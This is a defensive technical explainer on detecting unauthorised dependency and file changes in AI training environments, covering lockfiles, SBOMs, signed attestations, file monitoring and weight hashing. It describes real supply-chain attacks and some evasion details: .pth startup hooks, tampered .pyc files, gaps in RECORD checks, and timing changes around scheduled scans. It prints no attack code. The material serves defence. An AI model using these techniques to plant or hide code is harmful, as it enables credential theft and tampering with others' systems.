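# Detecting unauthorised software and dependency changes in AI development environments

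## What is an unauthorised change, and how does software enter an AI environment?

Detecting unauthorised software changes means comparing what is on a machine with what its owner agreed to have there. This comparison is difficult on machines that train and serve AI models. A training job draws on hundreds or thousands of packages by outside authors, container images (bundles of a program with the system software it needs), model files of many gigabytes, and often services that run on another company's servers. Any of these can change without anyone at the organisation deciding to change it.

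Some unauthorised changes are attacks. In November 2026 an attacker published two releases of agent-framework, Microsoft's official toolkit for building AI agents, with a credential stealer inside. The framework kept working as usual while the stealer ran in the background (Help Net Security, *Credential stealer slipped into Microsoft’s official Python agent framework*, 2026). Other changes are accidents, or updates that nobody reviewed.

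### Definitions

A dependency is anything a job needs that its authors did not write, such as a package, container image, model file or remote service. A transitive dependency is one that another dependency needs and that nobody on the team chose directly.

Most of the code in an AI system arrives indirectly, as dependencies of the software its developers chose. *The Grand Software Supply Chain of AI Systems* (Cesarano and Monperrus, 2026) examines a reference stack of 48 open-source projects that covers every function from collecting data to serving a model. It includes only projects whose production use is documented by a primary source, and resolves their dependencies with each project's own package manager. The 48 projects declare 4,664 packages directly and resolve to 11,508 transitive ones. The projects themselves contain 82.6 million lines of code and the transitive packages add another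 309 million, or nearly four lines for every line in the projects. These counts are probably best treated as order-of-magnitude estimates, because a single fine-tuning run would load only part of the stack, while the counts omit the transitive dependencies of C and C++ components and anything loaded only at run time, including GPU drivers.

A hash is a short fingerprint that a program computes from a file's bytes; if any byte changes, so does the hash. The approved set is the recorded list of dependencies, with exact versions and hashes, that an organisation has agreed may be present. Write A for the approved set and O for the set that somebody observes in the environment. The unauthorised changes U are then everything observed but not approved, plus every approved item whose hash differs from the recorded one:

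U = (O − A) ∪ {x in O ∩ A : observed hash of x ≠ approved hash of x}

Suppose A holds packages a, b and c, and a scan finds a, b, c and d, with an unexpected hash for b. Then U contains b and d. An upgraded package counts as a new item because the list specifies exact versions. A removed item does not appear in U, so finding a deleted safety filter, for example, requires the opposite subtraction, A − O.

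The formula does not include intent. Similarly, *Securing the AI Supply Chain* (2025) counts any "adversarial or accidental" condition as an AI security issue if it undermines the confidentiality, integrity or availability of AI systems. This breadth is useful because a change may mean that results are no longer comparable with last week's, even when nobody has attacked anything. For example, when NVIDIA patches one of its shared base images, every training job and deployment that inherits from the image changes at the same time, and a new GPU driver can alter how training converges. An accident and an attack can also look identical at the moment of detection, because either can appear as an unexpected file or a wrong hash.

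The source of the reference hash also matters. In March 2026 attackers used legitimate publishing credentials to release a malicious version of LiteLLM, a library that gives applications one interface to many language models. Snyk's *How a Poisoned Security Scanner Became the Key to Backdooring LiteLLM* explains that pip, the standard Python installer, accepted the package because its own file list included the malicious file with its correct hash. A hash that ships with a package shows only that the download matches what someone uploaded with the publisher's credentials. Exposing the substitution requires a hash recorded earlier, at approval.

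### What sets AI environments apart

AI environments share long dependency lists and careless updates with ordinary software. They differ most in their model weights, the learned numbers that determine what a model does. Cesarano and Monperrus separate "symbolic" artifacts, such as container images and training scripts, from "trained" ones, such as weights. A reviewer can read a script or compare two versions line by line, but nobody can work out a model's behaviour by inspecting its weights.

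An independent party can sometimes verify conventional software by recompiling the source and checking that the result is bit-for-bit identical. Retraining a model does not allow the same check, because training depends on the order in which GPUs schedule work and on floating-point rounding. Two runs of the same procedure on the same machine give different weights, so a mismatch is not evidence of tampering. A weight file's hash therefore identifies the file but not how it was produced. Comparing O with A can detect a swap made after approval, but not a backdoor that was already in the approved copy.

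Cesarano and Monperrus also describe dependencies that no package manager records. An adapter (a small file of extra weights from fine-tuning) works properly only with the exact base model it was trained on, and a search index only with the embedding model that produced its entries. Two approved items can therefore form a combination that nobody tested. An approved set for AI work should arguably list these pairings as well as files, because a mismatched model usually returns plausible answers of lower quality instead of crashing the program, as a mismatched library tends to do.

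*Securing the AI Agent* (2026) describes the inference servers, workflow tools and gateways around language models as new, fast-changing and often used outside hardened production environments. An approved list of such software soon goes out of date, and teams are always tempted to accept whatever is newest.

These environments also hold API keys and model weights that attackers may want. A gateway library like LiteLLM sits between applications and several AI providers, so it often has access to the keys for all of them, as researchers at the security company Sonatype point out in Help Net Security's *LiteLLM PyPI packages compromised in expanding TeamPCP supply chain attacks* (2026). Business Standard's *Hackers target AI supply chains as stolen tokens fuel new cyber threat* quotes Unit 42, the research group of Palo Alto Networks, on thieves who use stolen keys to resell AI computing through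 intermediaries, and on companies that lost millions of dollars in charges before they noticed. An intruder on an unprotected inference server can also copy or poison the model weights.

### Routes of entry

Most software arrives through a package manager, and a loose version requirement can let in an unapproved release. A project that requires agent-framework 1.26 or later accepts any newer release as soon as it is published. According to Aikido's *Two malicious agent-framework releases hit PyPI in 33 minutes*, two malicious versions of agent-framework were available on the Python Package Index (PyPI), the public registry of Python packages, for about 45 minutes on 17 November 2026. Any automated build that resolved its dependencies afresh during that time could have installed one of them, even though nobody had edited the project.

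Installing a package can run code. npm, the package manager for JavaScript, lets packages declare scripts that run during installation. The Hacker News' *Mini Shai-Hulud Worm Compromises TanStack, Mistral AI, Guardrails AI & More Packages* (2026) describes two variants of this attack from one campaign. In Mistral AI's npm packages, the attackers added a script that ran before installation, downloaded the JavaScript runtime Bun and used it to launch a credential stealer. In TanStack's packages, they added an optional dependency hosted on GitHub, and that dependency's own script launched the stealer. A reviewer who checked only the install scripts of the packages on the team's list would have missed the TanStack variant.

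Python's prebuilt packages run no script at installation, but attackers get much the same effect from a startup hook, a file that Python runs whenever the interpreter starts. According to *site* in the Python documentation, Python looks in its package directories at each start for files whose names end in .pth. These files mainly list further directories to search, but for backward compatibility Python also executes any line in them that begins with "import", even if the program never uses the package that installed the file. Both the LiteLLM and the agent-framework attacks used such a file.

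Python 3.15 deprecated executable lines in .pth files, and versions 3.18 and 3.19 will ignore those lines. Their replacement is a file ending in .start that names a function to call. A named function is easier for a reviewer to inspect than an arbitrary string of code, but a malicious installed package can still run code at startup. When Python's Steering Council accepted the proposal, *PEP 829*, it asked for an explicit acknowledgement that this threat is unchanged. Python also tries to import two modules at startup, sitecustomize and usercustomize, so a check that covers only .pth files misses other ways to run code at startup.

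Container images bring in many dependencies at once. A build recipe may stack several upstream images and install packages from several registries, and Cesarano and Monperrus note that no single manifest then declares everything in the finished image. Attackers have used container images as well as package registries. In *LiteLLM Compromised in Fresh Supply Chain Attack*, Arghire (2026) reports malicious LiteLLM packages on both PyPI and the container platform Docker in October 2026.

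Build pipelines are the automated jobs that test, assemble and publish software, including packages and images. They commonly run "actions", which are reusable steps written by outside authors, and they hold credentials for registries and production clusters. An attacker who controls a pipeline can insert code into its output and still obtain a valid signature, because the legitimate build system produced the file. The March attack on LiteLLM began this way, with a compromised security scanner.

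Model files can carry code as well as numbers. Pickle, for years the usual format for weights in the PyTorch framework, lets a file call functions while it loads. In February 2024 researchers disclosed roughly a hundred models on Hugging Face, the main public hub for open models, that ran arbitrary code on any machine that loaded them. A model's repository may also contain Python scripts, for instance to define an unusual architecture, which the loading library downloads and runs if the user permits it. Approval of the weights does not cover a script in the same folder, which needs its own entry and hash.

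People also add software by hand. A researcher who types an install command into a notebook, an interactive document of code and results, changes the environment without updating the project's dependency list. A coding agent, a program that writes and runs code on a developer's behalf, can issue the same commands, perhaps many in one session, while the developer looks only at the outcome. Both people and agents can install a malicious package by getting a name slightly wrong. SC Media's *Mini Shai-Hulud ‘Hades’ variant affects 23 PyPI package versions* describes attackers who registered misspellings such as "rsquests" and plausible made-up names such as "langchain-core-mcp". Malware can also hide in coding agents. In the Mistral AI campaign, it planted hooks in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, so that it would run again at later launches.

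Finally, a job may fetch datasets, documents for retrieval, or more code while it runs. The langchain-core-mcp package contained a startup hook that searched for a malicious script, but the package did not include the script itself, so a scan of the package alone would have found only the hook. Researchers at the security company Socket suspected that the attackers meant to deliver the script separately.

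### Stored, memory-only and remote changes

Where a change ends up matters more for detection than how it got there. A stored change leaves new or altered bytes on disk. In a memory-only change, a process fetches code and runs it without saving it as a file. In a remote change, a service that the job calls is altered, but nothing changes on the local machine.

A file monitor compares file hashes, so it can detect a stored change that a reader of the source code would miss. Some of the Hades packages hid their trigger in a compiled extension, which a scan of Python source cannot read, but the extension was still a new file with a new hash. A change made only in memory leaves no changed file for the monitor to compare. Detecting it requires recording what the process does as it runs, such as the programs it starts and the connections it opens, because the code disappears when the process ends.

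Local monitoring of files and processes cannot detect a remote change, because the job still sends the same kind of request to the same address. Only the answers differ, and they may differ for innocent reasons. Cesarano and Monperrus cite a study in which GPT-4's accuracy at identifying prime numbers fell from 84% to 51% over three months. Users had no public changelog and could not return to an earlier version.

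One attack can involve more than one kind of change. Suppose a team fine-tunes a base model with 70 billion parameters, whose weights occupy 140 GB at two bytes per parameter. The team installs packages from a lockfile, which fixes the exact version and hash of each one. During training, the job sends sample outputs over the network to a grader, a model hosted by another company that scores them, and the team keeps the version of its own model with the best scores. The approved set lists the packages, the container image and the weight files with their hashes, but it lists the grader only by name and address because the provider publishes no hash.

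Three things then go wrong. A researcher manually installs a plotting package from a notebook on the training machine, outside the lockfile, and one of the package's transitive dependencies adds a startup hook. The next time Python starts, the hook downloads a second-stage script and runs it in memory. The script reads the team's access keys and sends them out. Some days later, in an unrelated change, the grader's provider replaces the grader model but keeps its name. The new grader is more lenient, but the job reports no error, so the team keeps a model that the old grader would have scored lower.

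| Change | Kind | What is different | Where evidence can be found |
|---|---|---|---|
| Startup hook | Stored | A new file in Python's package directory | The file system |
| Second-stage script | Memory-only | Code inside a running process | Process activity and network traffic |
| Replaced grader | Remote | The model behind an approved name | The grader's answers |

If O is a list of files, the formula for U returns the plotting package, the dependency that came with it and the hook. It returns the script only if O also includes the code that processes are running. It cannot return the grader, because the grader's name and address still match the approved entry.

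## What do lockfiles, bills of materials and signatures prove?

To compare a machine with its approved set, someone must first record that set. Lockfiles, software bills of materials and signatures each supply part of the record. A lockfile fixes which bytes an installer may accept, a bill of materials lists what a piece of software contains, and a signature links a file to its publisher.

### Lockfiles

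The simplest lockfile for Python is a list of exact versions with one or more hashes for each. pip's *Secure installs* gives the following entry as an example (the dots replace the middle of each hash):

```
FooProject == 1.2 \
  --hash=sha256:2cf24dba...938b9824 \
  --hash=sha256:486ea462...0e9cb8a7
```

The entry allows only version 1.2 of FooProject. It accepts two files because a release often includes separate builds for different platforms. At install time, pip queries the package index for the version 1.2 files and discards any whose advertised hash is not in the entry. It downloads one of the remaining files, computes the SHA-256 hash of the downloaded bytes, and compares it with the hashes in the entry. If it matches neither, pip stops with an error.

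Only the comparison after the download protects the user. The index supplies the advertised hash, so an attacker who controls the index can advertise the approved hash and send a different file. For the same reason, pip does not accept a hash from the index in place of one in the local file.

A server may offer different bytes under the same version number. If it has replaced the approved file, the download's hash does not match and the installation fails. If it has added a new file beside the approved one, pip ignores the new file and installs the approved one. Before a code change in 2019, pip could choose the new file and fail with a hash error. In a GitHub discussion, users installing certbot on Raspberry Pi computers reported such errors, because pip had chosen builds whose hashes were not in their lists. Nobody had attacked those users, so a hash error is a reason to investigate but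 not yet evidence of tampering.

A project that pins the version but records no hashes has neither protection. An attacker with a maintainer's credentials could add a file to an old, trusted release, and pip might install it instead of the original. PyPI reduced this risk in July 2026, when it began rejecting new files for releases more than 14 days old. The change seems to have caused maintainers little inconvenience. According to PyPI's *Releases now reject new files after 14 days* (2026), only 56 of the top 15,000 projects had added a Python 3.14 build to a release more than 14 days old.

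Hash checking is of little use if it covers only some packages, since an attacker can use one that has no hash. If the lockfile contains even one hash, pip therefore requires an exact version and a hash for every package, including transitive dependencies. Since version 26.2, users can turn this rule off, for instance to combine hashed packages with code from a local directory. Even with hash checking on, installing from a source archive runs code from that archive, so pip's documentation recommends also allowing only prebuilt packages. A developer who runs a project's setup.py file directly, as was once common, bypasses the lockfile, because that command downloads missing dependencies without checking them.

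A lockfile also protects only against changes made after it is created. pip can print the hashes of the packages it has just fetched, which is a convenient way to start a list, but those hashes will match whatever the server sent, including any malicious files. A team that regenerated its lockfile during the 45 minutes when the malicious agent-framework releases were on PyPI could have recorded a malicious file's hash, and every later installation would have passed the check.

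### Bills of materials

A lockfile specifies what an installer should fetch. A software bill of materials (SBOM) is a machine-readable inventory for later use, for example by a customer checking whether a product contains a vulnerable library. Most SBOMs use one of two formats, SPDX or CycloneDX. The US National Telecommunications and Information Administration (NTIA) set out seven minimum fields: each component's supplier, name, version, other unique identifier and dependency relationships, plus the SBOM's author and when it was created.

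*Beyond Compliance* (Bhuiyan, Besbes and colleagues, 2026) examined the SBOMs that GitHub generates automatically for 10,000 popular repositories in ten programming languages. None met the NTIA minimum, because the supplier's name was missing. The NTIA minimum's seven fields also do not include a hash, which is a more serious gap for detecting changes. An SBOM with only those fields can show that version 1.2 is present where the approved set has 1.1, but not that somebody altered the bytes of version 1.2.

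An AI bill of materials extends the inventory to datasets, model weights and training pipelines. Version 3.0 of SPDX introduced profiles for AI models and datasets (Pepe and D'Amici, 2026, *AIGen*). The schema in *AI Bill of Materials and Beyond* (2025) has ten categories, with fields for a model's hardware requirements, software dependencies and their permitted versions, training data sources, and test set sizes. Datasets are often too sensitive to include in such a document. *Operationalising Artificial Intelligence Bills of Materials (AIBOMs) for Verifiable AI Provenance* (2026) proposes recording a reference to the data, a description of how developers transformed it, and a cryptographic link. If the link is a hash, an auditor with access to the dataset can check that it matches the one recorded.

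Many of these inventories repeat what a model's publisher wrote. *A Large-Scale Measurement of AI Bill of Materials Completeness* (2026) used a generator for models on Hugging Face that draws on the repository's metadata, configuration, licence details and model card, which is the publisher's own description of the model. Pepe and D'Amici's tool works from MLflow, a system developers use to log training runs, and fills in the inventory partly with fixed rules and partly with a language model. If an attacker replaced the weights but left the model card alone, an inventory made from the card would not change.

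For detection, how an inventory was made therefore matters more than its format. A declared inventory comes from files in which developers state what their software needs. An installed inventory lists the packages present in the environment, as the command "pip freeze" does for Python. A loaded inventory covers only what a running program has imported. In the earlier example, a researcher installed a plotting package from a notebook. That package is missing from the declared inventory because no project file mentions it, but it appears in the installed one. It may be missing from the loaded inventory of a training job that never draws a plot, even though the package's startup hook runs in that job.

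*Modelstamp* (Dhekne, 2026) describes a tool that stores a model file's hash and the installed versions of a fixed set of packages when a developer saves the model. It checks both before anyone loads the model again. It compares only the packages that its rules treat as relevant to that model, to avoid warning about every unrelated upgrade. In 14 controlled scenarios, it warned about the relevant changes and ignored the others. Dhekne designed both the rules and the scenarios, so the result shows that the tool works as intended but gives little idea of how many real changes it would catch. The tool would probably miss the plotting package, which has nothing to do with the model.

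### How accurate are generated inventories?

Studies of Python projects have found large errors in declared inventories. Bhuiyan and colleagues randomly sampled 200 Python repositories from their collection and installed each project's dependencies in a clean environment. They then listed the installed packages with pip freeze and compared the list with the output of four SBOM generators.

| Generator | Share of listed packages that were installed | Share of installed packages that it listed | Correct version, among packages it found |
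|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft SBOM Tool | 44.4% | 66.4% | 69.8% |
| GitHub SBOM Tool | 33.7% | 57.3% | 21.6% |
| Syft | 13.2% | 34.1% | 31.0% |
| Trivy | 20.3% | 32.3% | 27.4% |

The figures are averages across repositories. Even the best generator missed a third of the installed packages, and more than half of the packages it listed were not installed. Multiplying its averages (0.664 × 0.698) suggests that it gave the right name and version for roughly 46% of installed packages.

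Some of the errors arise because projects do not specify exact versions. A clean installation then picks a compatible version available that day, and the study counted any other version, or a range of versions, as an error. Bhuiyan and colleagues also looked at 9,575 cases in which GitHub's tool gave no version for a Python library. In 62% of them, the requirements file listed the library without a version, and in the other 38% it did not list the library at all. GitHub's tool did much better on JavaScript, where it found 86.7% of packages and got 90.4% of their versions right. But the JavaScript sample included only repositories with a lockfile, and the researchers checked the tool's output against that same lockfile, so the result mainly shows that the tool can copy a lockfile well.

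*SBOM Generation Tools in the Python Ecosystem* (2024) traces many errors to generators that do not read lockfiles, leave out packages without an exact version, or guess the version. *A Large Scale Empirical Analysis on the Adherence Gap* (2026) points out that a generator may also miss dependencies listed in a file called install.txt because it looks for requirements.txt.

Benedetti, Cofano and colleagues (2024), in *The Impact of SBOM Generators on Vulnerability Assessment in Python*, measured how such errors affect security scans. They produced SBOMs for 1,000 PyPI packages with five generators, ran a vulnerability scanner on them, and compared its findings with the known vulnerabilities in a real installation of each package. With SBOMs from the best generator, cdxgen, an average of 17% of the reported vulnerabilities were real, and the scanner found 21% of the real ones. These percentages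 count vulnerabilities, so they aren't comparable with the table's figures for packages. When the researchers investigated the false alarms, they found that an average of 75% of the dependencies in the SBOMs were not installed.

Benedetti and colleagues then built a generator into pip that uses pip's own procedure for choosing packages to install. The two figures rose to 81% and 80%. The comparison somewhat favours their tool, because pip also produced the reference installation. Still, cdxgen, the best of the five existing generators, also installs dependencies before listing them, which supports the view that inventories should come from the installer or the environment rather than from project files.

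The effect of an error depends on whether the inventory serves as the approved set A or the observed set O. Suppose a team uses the Microsoft tool's output as A for an environment with 300 installed packages. At the average rates in the table, A would omit about 100 of those packages, and each omission would cause a false alarm. A would also include about 250 packages that nobody had installed. If an attacker later added one of these at the listed version, a comparison of names and versions would not detect it. If the team used the tool to produce O instead, a package that somebody installed by hand would never appear in it. It is better to take A from a lockfile and O from the environment. *A Reality Check on SBOM-based Vulnerability Management* (2025) similarly uses lockfiles as the standard for judging SBOM generators.

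### How signing works

Checking a hash does not detect tampering when an attacker supplies both the file and the hash, as in the March attack on LiteLLM. Such a substitution is harder if the producer and the checker share a secret key, but Dhekne notes that everyone who holds the key can produce a valid record. With a public signature, one party signs with a private key and anyone can verify the result. The traditional weakness of this method is that the private key may exist for years, which gives attackers time to steal it.

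Sigstore, a public signing service, avoids long-lived keys, and PyPI has built its attestations on it. An attestation is a signed statement about an artifact, here a package file. The signer is usually an automated publishing workflow and not a person. PyPI's *Security model and considerations* describes the procedure, which runs as follows for a project on GitHub:

1. The workflow obtains a token from GitHub that identifies the repository and the workflow.
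2. It creates a temporary pair of keys and sends the public key, together with the token, to Sigstore's certificate authority, Fulcio.
3. Fulcio checks the token and issues a short-lived certificate that links the public key to the workflow's identity.
4. The workflow writes a statement with the package's file name and SHA-256 hash and signs it with the private key. It can then throw the key away.
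5. Sigstore records the signature in a public log, Rekor. A second log lists the certificates that Fulcio issues, so a project can look for signatures in its name that it did not make.

The statement uses in-toto, a common format for claims about software. It binds a file's name and hash to the repository that produced the file, according to Trail of Bits' *Attestations* (2024). The basic PyPI attestation contains only the claim that an authorised publisher published the file. Other statements can include more about the build. SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) is a framework for such build records, known in SLSA as provenance. According to *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* (2026), a SLSA record covers the identity of the build system, the build instructions and parameters, the environment variables, and the hashes of the dependencies.

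SLSA's build levels describe how hard a build's provenance record is to fake. At level 1 the record exists, but a developer could have written it by hand. At level 2 a hosted build service generates and signs it. At level 3 the service must also isolate builds from one another and keep the signing key away from the build steps that the project defines. A higher level gives more reason to believe the record, but it is not a rating of the code.

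The Python Packaging User Guide's *Index hosted attestations* lists the checks a program must make to verify a PyPI attestation. The attestation's certificate must come from an authority that the program already trusts, and it must name an appropriate signer. The file name and hash in the attestation's statement must match the file. The signature must be valid for that statement and that certificate. The program may also require an entry in a public log, in which case it must check that the time of the entry falls within the certificate's short validity period. PyPI requires proofs from both of Sigstore's logs.

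Checking the signer requires knowing which identity to expect. For a GitHub project, this is a specific workflow file in a specific repository, such as release.yml in pypa/sampleproject, an example from PyPI's *attestation internals*. A user could take the identity from PyPI, but would then have no independent record if an attacker changed the project's settings there. Python's standard lockfile format, pylock.toml, can store each package's publisher at the time of locking, according to snarky.ca's *Why pylock.toml includes digital attestations*, and a tool can later compare this record with the publisher listed on the index.

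As of May 2026, neither pip nor uv checked these publisher identities when installing packages, according to the Python Developer Tooling Handbook's *Why pylock.toml Includes Digital Attestations*. The main safeguard was a human reviewer noticing that a publisher had changed or disappeared in a proposed lockfile update.

Most packages have no attestation to check. *Reproducibility is Not Enough* (2026) found attestations for between 2.0% and 6.6% of the latest package versions in four public registries, including PyPI and npm. *A Difference Without a Distinction* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) found a much higher share, 40%, among sampled PyPI packages. The two results are compatible because Santos-Grueiro sampled packages that release regularly and counted any release since April 2024 rather than only the latest. Attestations are common among active projects but rare among the many less active packages,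 some of which will be transitive dependencies.

### From "signed by the official pipeline" to "safe"

PyPI's documentation warns users not to treat an attestation as proof that a package is trustworthy. A valid signature shows that whoever built the package had access to the publisher's identity at the time. To conclude that the package is safe, a user must also make several assumptions that the signature doesn't verify: that the package was built from source code the maintainers had reviewed, that nobody had altered the workflow, that the build tools and dependencies were clean, and that the maintainers had made no harmful change.

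In 2024, attackers published two malicious versions of Ultralytics, a widely used computer-vision package, through the project's own workflow. They uploaded two more with an API token that the project had not revoked, and these lacked the usual attestations. A rule requiring attestations would have blocked the second pair but accepted the first. Martin-Jones reports in *Introducing PyPI digital attestation support* that responders could still use the attestations to audit what had happened.

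A detailed build record may also contain evidence of tampering that a simple signature check misses. In October 2026, attackers made LiteLLM's official pipeline build and sign a malicious release from a lookalike repository (IT-Administrator's *LiteLLM* describes the signed packages). Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (2026) reports that the build records for the container image named the source as Berri-AI/litellm instead of BerriAI/litellm. Anyone who compared the recorded source with the expected one could have noticed the extra hyphen.

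Rebuilding a package from its official source can expose code added during the build, though not malicious code in the source itself. The verifier must first find that source, but *Reproducibility is Not Enough* reports that between 14.7% and 42.4% of packages, depending on the registry, have no valid link to a repository.

Attestations are more useful for detecting a change in how a project publishes. Santos-Grueiro tested an optional rule in pnpm, a JavaScript package manager, that refuses a release if its evidence of origin is weaker than that of an earlier release of the same package. He reconstructed 12 attacks that used stolen publishing credentials, ten on npm and two on PyPI, and replayed the rule on their 41 malicious releases. It flagged 17 releases, from five attacks. Only those five attacks hit packages that had previously published attestations or similar evidence, which the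 rule needs for comparison. In a wider count of 1,654 attacked npm packages, only 17.5% had such a history.

The replay probably overstates how well the rule works. The rule checks whether evidence is present, but not whether it points to the right project, and Santos-Grueiro estimates that the attackers could have got 15 of the 17 releases past it by adding evidence of their own. In the wider count, the rule also flagged none of the 119 malicious versions of 46 packages that attackers published through the projects' own trusted workflows.

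The rule also blocked legitimate software. With it switched on, pnpm could not install the latest version of 16 of the 1,000 most popular npm packages, or of 76 of 997 recently updated ones. A single security fix to the package semver caused 14 of the 16 failures. A maintainer had published the fix by hand for users of an older version, without the provenance that newer versions carried, and the rule could not distinguish this from a takeover.

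Comparing signers more strictly has a similar problem. A certificate names the workflow and the exact branch or version tag, so its text can change with every ordinary release. An alarm on any difference went off for 75.8% of packages with at least two signed releases, and for 13.9% when it ignored the branch and tag. Refusing every release less than a day old would have worked better than pnpm's rule against the reconstructed attacks. It would have kept out 36 of the 41 malicious releases, because most disappeared from the registry within hours.

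### Rules and official guidance

In the European Union, the AI Act has imposed duties on providers of general-purpose AI models since 2 August 2025, and the Commission has been able to enforce them with fines since 2 August 2026. Providers whose models pose systemic risks must also protect the model and its physical infrastructure against cyber threats. Providers can show compliance by following the voluntary Code of Practice of 10 July 2025, but its chapter on safety and security applies only to those whose models pose systemic risks, as Arab48's *قانون الذكاء الاصطناعي الأوروبي يدخل اختبار الإنفاذ العملي* (2026) explains. In late August 2026 the Commission used its powers for the first time to demand information from leading developers about cybersecurity, safety and copyright, according to Euractiv's *L'UE demande aux développeurs d'IA de détailler leurs pratiques de sécurité*. Mondaq's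 *The European Commission’s First Use Of EU AI Act Investigatory Powers* adds that the security requests covered independent evaluations and the monitoring of models after release. The Commission was still reviewing the replies in October, and a request does not imply that a company has broken the law.

The EU's Cyber Resilience Act, a 2024 regulation on hardware and software products, requires manufacturers to draw up a software bill of materials (SBOM) in a common machine-readable format that covers at least the top-level dependencies. Under the text as adopted, this duty applies from 11 December 2027, while the duty to report actively exploited vulnerabilities began on 11 September 2026. A list of top-level dependencies could omit much of an AI system, because most of its packages are transitive dependencies. In the United States, the cybersecurity agency CISA published a draft update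 of the NTIA minimum SBOM fields in August 2025. The draft would add a hash for each component, which would let users check for altered bytes as well as unexpected names and versions.

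## What can file monitoring detect?

A lockfile controls what an installer accepts, but files can still change after installation. File integrity monitoring detects these changes by comparing hashes of the current files with hashes recorded earlier. It can detect almost any change saved to disk, provided that it covers the right files and the earlier hashes are trustworthy.

### Baselines and scans

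The method goes back to Tripwire, a program that Gene Kim and Eugene Spafford wrote at Purdue University in 1992. In a series of break-ins the year before, intruders had altered shared libraries, the code that many programs load, without changing the libraries' checksums. The checksums were CRCs, which catch accidental errors, but an attacker can match them by adjusting a few bytes. Tripwire used cryptographic hashes, which are much harder to match, and could store several kinds of hash for each file in case one proved weak. Researchers later broke MD5, one of the original choices.

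A monitor of this type works in four steps:

1. An administrator writes a policy that names the files and directories to check and the attributes to compare, such as contents, size and permissions.
2. The monitor hashes the files and stores the results as a baseline.
3. At each later scan, it computes the hashes again and reports every file that has appeared, disappeared or changed.
4. The administrator investigates each difference or accepts it, and accepted differences go into the baseline.

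The baseline is the part of the approved set A that concerns files, and each scan produces a new observed set O. The policy has to exclude files that change constantly, such as logs and, on a training machine, caches and checkpoints (saved copies of a model in training). File monitoring therefore misses malware in any directory the policy excludes.

If the monitor scans every T hours and a change is equally likely to happen at any moment between two scans, the delay before the next scan ranges from 0 to T hours and averages T/2. Daily scans therefore detect a lasting change after 12 hours on average, and hourly scans after 30 minutes.

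Periodic scans may miss a temporary change. If scans run every T hours and an attacker alters a file and restores it d hours later, where d is less than T, the probability that a scan occurs while the file is altered is d/T. For a 45-minute change under daily scans, this is 0.75/24, or about 3%. An attacker who knows the schedule can reduce it to zero. Linux also records a change time for each file, which ordinary programs cannot set. A monitor that compares change times may therefore report that something touched the file, but it cannot recover the altered contents after the attacker has restored the original.

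### Kernel notifications

Linux can also report each change to a monitor as it happens. A program can use an interface called inotify to register a directory with the kernel, which then queues an event whenever another program creates, writes, renames or deletes a file there. The monitor can then hash the file immediately, which usually cuts the delay to less than a second. A change produces an event even if somebody later reverses it. A newer interface, fanotify, also identifies the process responsible and can block an attempt to open a file until the monitor allows it.

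Notifications can also miss changes. An inotify watch does not cover subdirectories, so the monitor must add one for each. If events arrive faster than the monitor reads them, the queue fills up and the kernel discards the rest, leaving only a marker that some are missing. inotify also does not report writes made through a memory-mapped file, and on a network file system it reports only changes made from the local machine. This last limit matters for AI clusters, where many machines often read their weights from shared storage, because another machine can replace a weight file without causing an event on the machine that loads it. It therefore makes sense to use notifications for speed and keep periodic scans to catch what they miss.

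### The startup hook

In the earlier example, a researcher installed a plotting package by hand, and one of its transitive dependencies added a startup hook to Python's package directory. A full scan would report the hook as a new file, but if scans ran daily, the report would come an average of 12 hours after the installation. Python runs the hook the next time anyone starts the interpreter, which may be seconds later on a busy training machine. The team would learn from the scan that they need to replace their access keys, but probably after the keys had been stolen.

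A notification would arrive during the installation, along with one for every other file the installer writes, and there may be thousands. A separate rule helps for the few file names that Python acts on at startup, such as .pth files and sitecustomize. Some legitimate packages, including the widely used setuptools, also install .pth files, so the approved set needs to list those.

Checking files against the lists that come with packages, instead of against a baseline, can miss the hook. For each package it installs, pip keeps a file called RECORD that lists the package's files, most of them with a hash. A checker can go through every RECORD and report any listed file that is missing or different. If the dependency itself installed the hook, its RECORD lists the hook with the correct hash, as in the March attack on LiteLLM, so the checker reports no problem. If malware wrote the hook separately,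 no RECORD lists it, and the checker never opens it. To find such a file, the checker must list the directory's contents and look for files that no RECORD lists.

RECORD also normally gives no hash for .pyc files, the compiled copies of modules that Python keeps to save time. By default, Python runs the compiled copy if the timestamp and size stored inside it match the source file. An attacker who edits the compiled copy can therefore change what a module does without changing the source file's hash. A baseline should cover the compiled files too, or the team should delete them and stop Python from loading or writing new ones.

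### Hashing model files

A program can hash a weight file even if the file is larger than the machine's memory. It reads one block, updates the hash and discards the block before reading the next. Dhekne's Modelstamp, which saves a record beside each model file, and *Caleta* (2026), a tool for running language models locally, both read 1 MiB at a time. Caleta starts a model only if the file's size and SHA-256 hash both match the declared values.

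Dhekne measured Modelstamp's speed at 307 to 312 MiB per second, with 3.3 seconds for a file of 1 GiB. At 310 MiB per second, the 140 GB of weights in the earlier example would take

140,000,000,000 / (310 × 1,048,576) ≈ 431 seconds,

or about seven minutes. This is an extrapolation, and perhaps an optimistic one. Dhekne's largest file was 1 GiB, and the test had already loaded it into the memory cache, so the disk played little part.

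Kliukovkin (2026), in *Cold-Start Model Delivery in Kubernetes Inference Serving*, measured how much time hashing adds to a model download, using 140 GB of mostly random data in place of the weights of a 70-billion-parameter model. On a cloud server with a disk limited to 125 MiB per second, the download took 2,220 seconds. Hashing the file afterwards added 1,186 seconds because the server had to read everything from the disk again. Hashing each block during the download added less than 0.1%, since the processor could hash data faster than the disk could store it. The first check of a large model can therefore add almost no time if it happens during the download, but a later check must read the whole file again.

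Later checks are still worthwhile, because insiders and intruders can alter a file after it arrives. *Sentry* (Gan and Ghodsi, 2025) mentions an intern at ByteDance who sabotaged the company's internal models, and argues for verification before every use if possible. Ordinary hashing makes this slow, because SHA-256 processes a long file in sequence, with each step needing the result of the one before. *Sentry* reports times of up to 26 seconds for GPT2-XL, which has only 1.6 billion parameters.

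Their system avoids this by building a Merkle tree. It hashes each block separately, then repeatedly hashes the results in pairs until one value remains. A GPU can hash many blocks at once, and Gan and Ghodsi report hashing models up to 269 times as fast as their CPU baseline. Updating the tree also takes little computation. A 140 GB file contains about 133,500 blocks of 1 MiB, so the tree has 18 levels above the blocks. After a change to one block, the program needs to recompute only that block's hash and 18 others.

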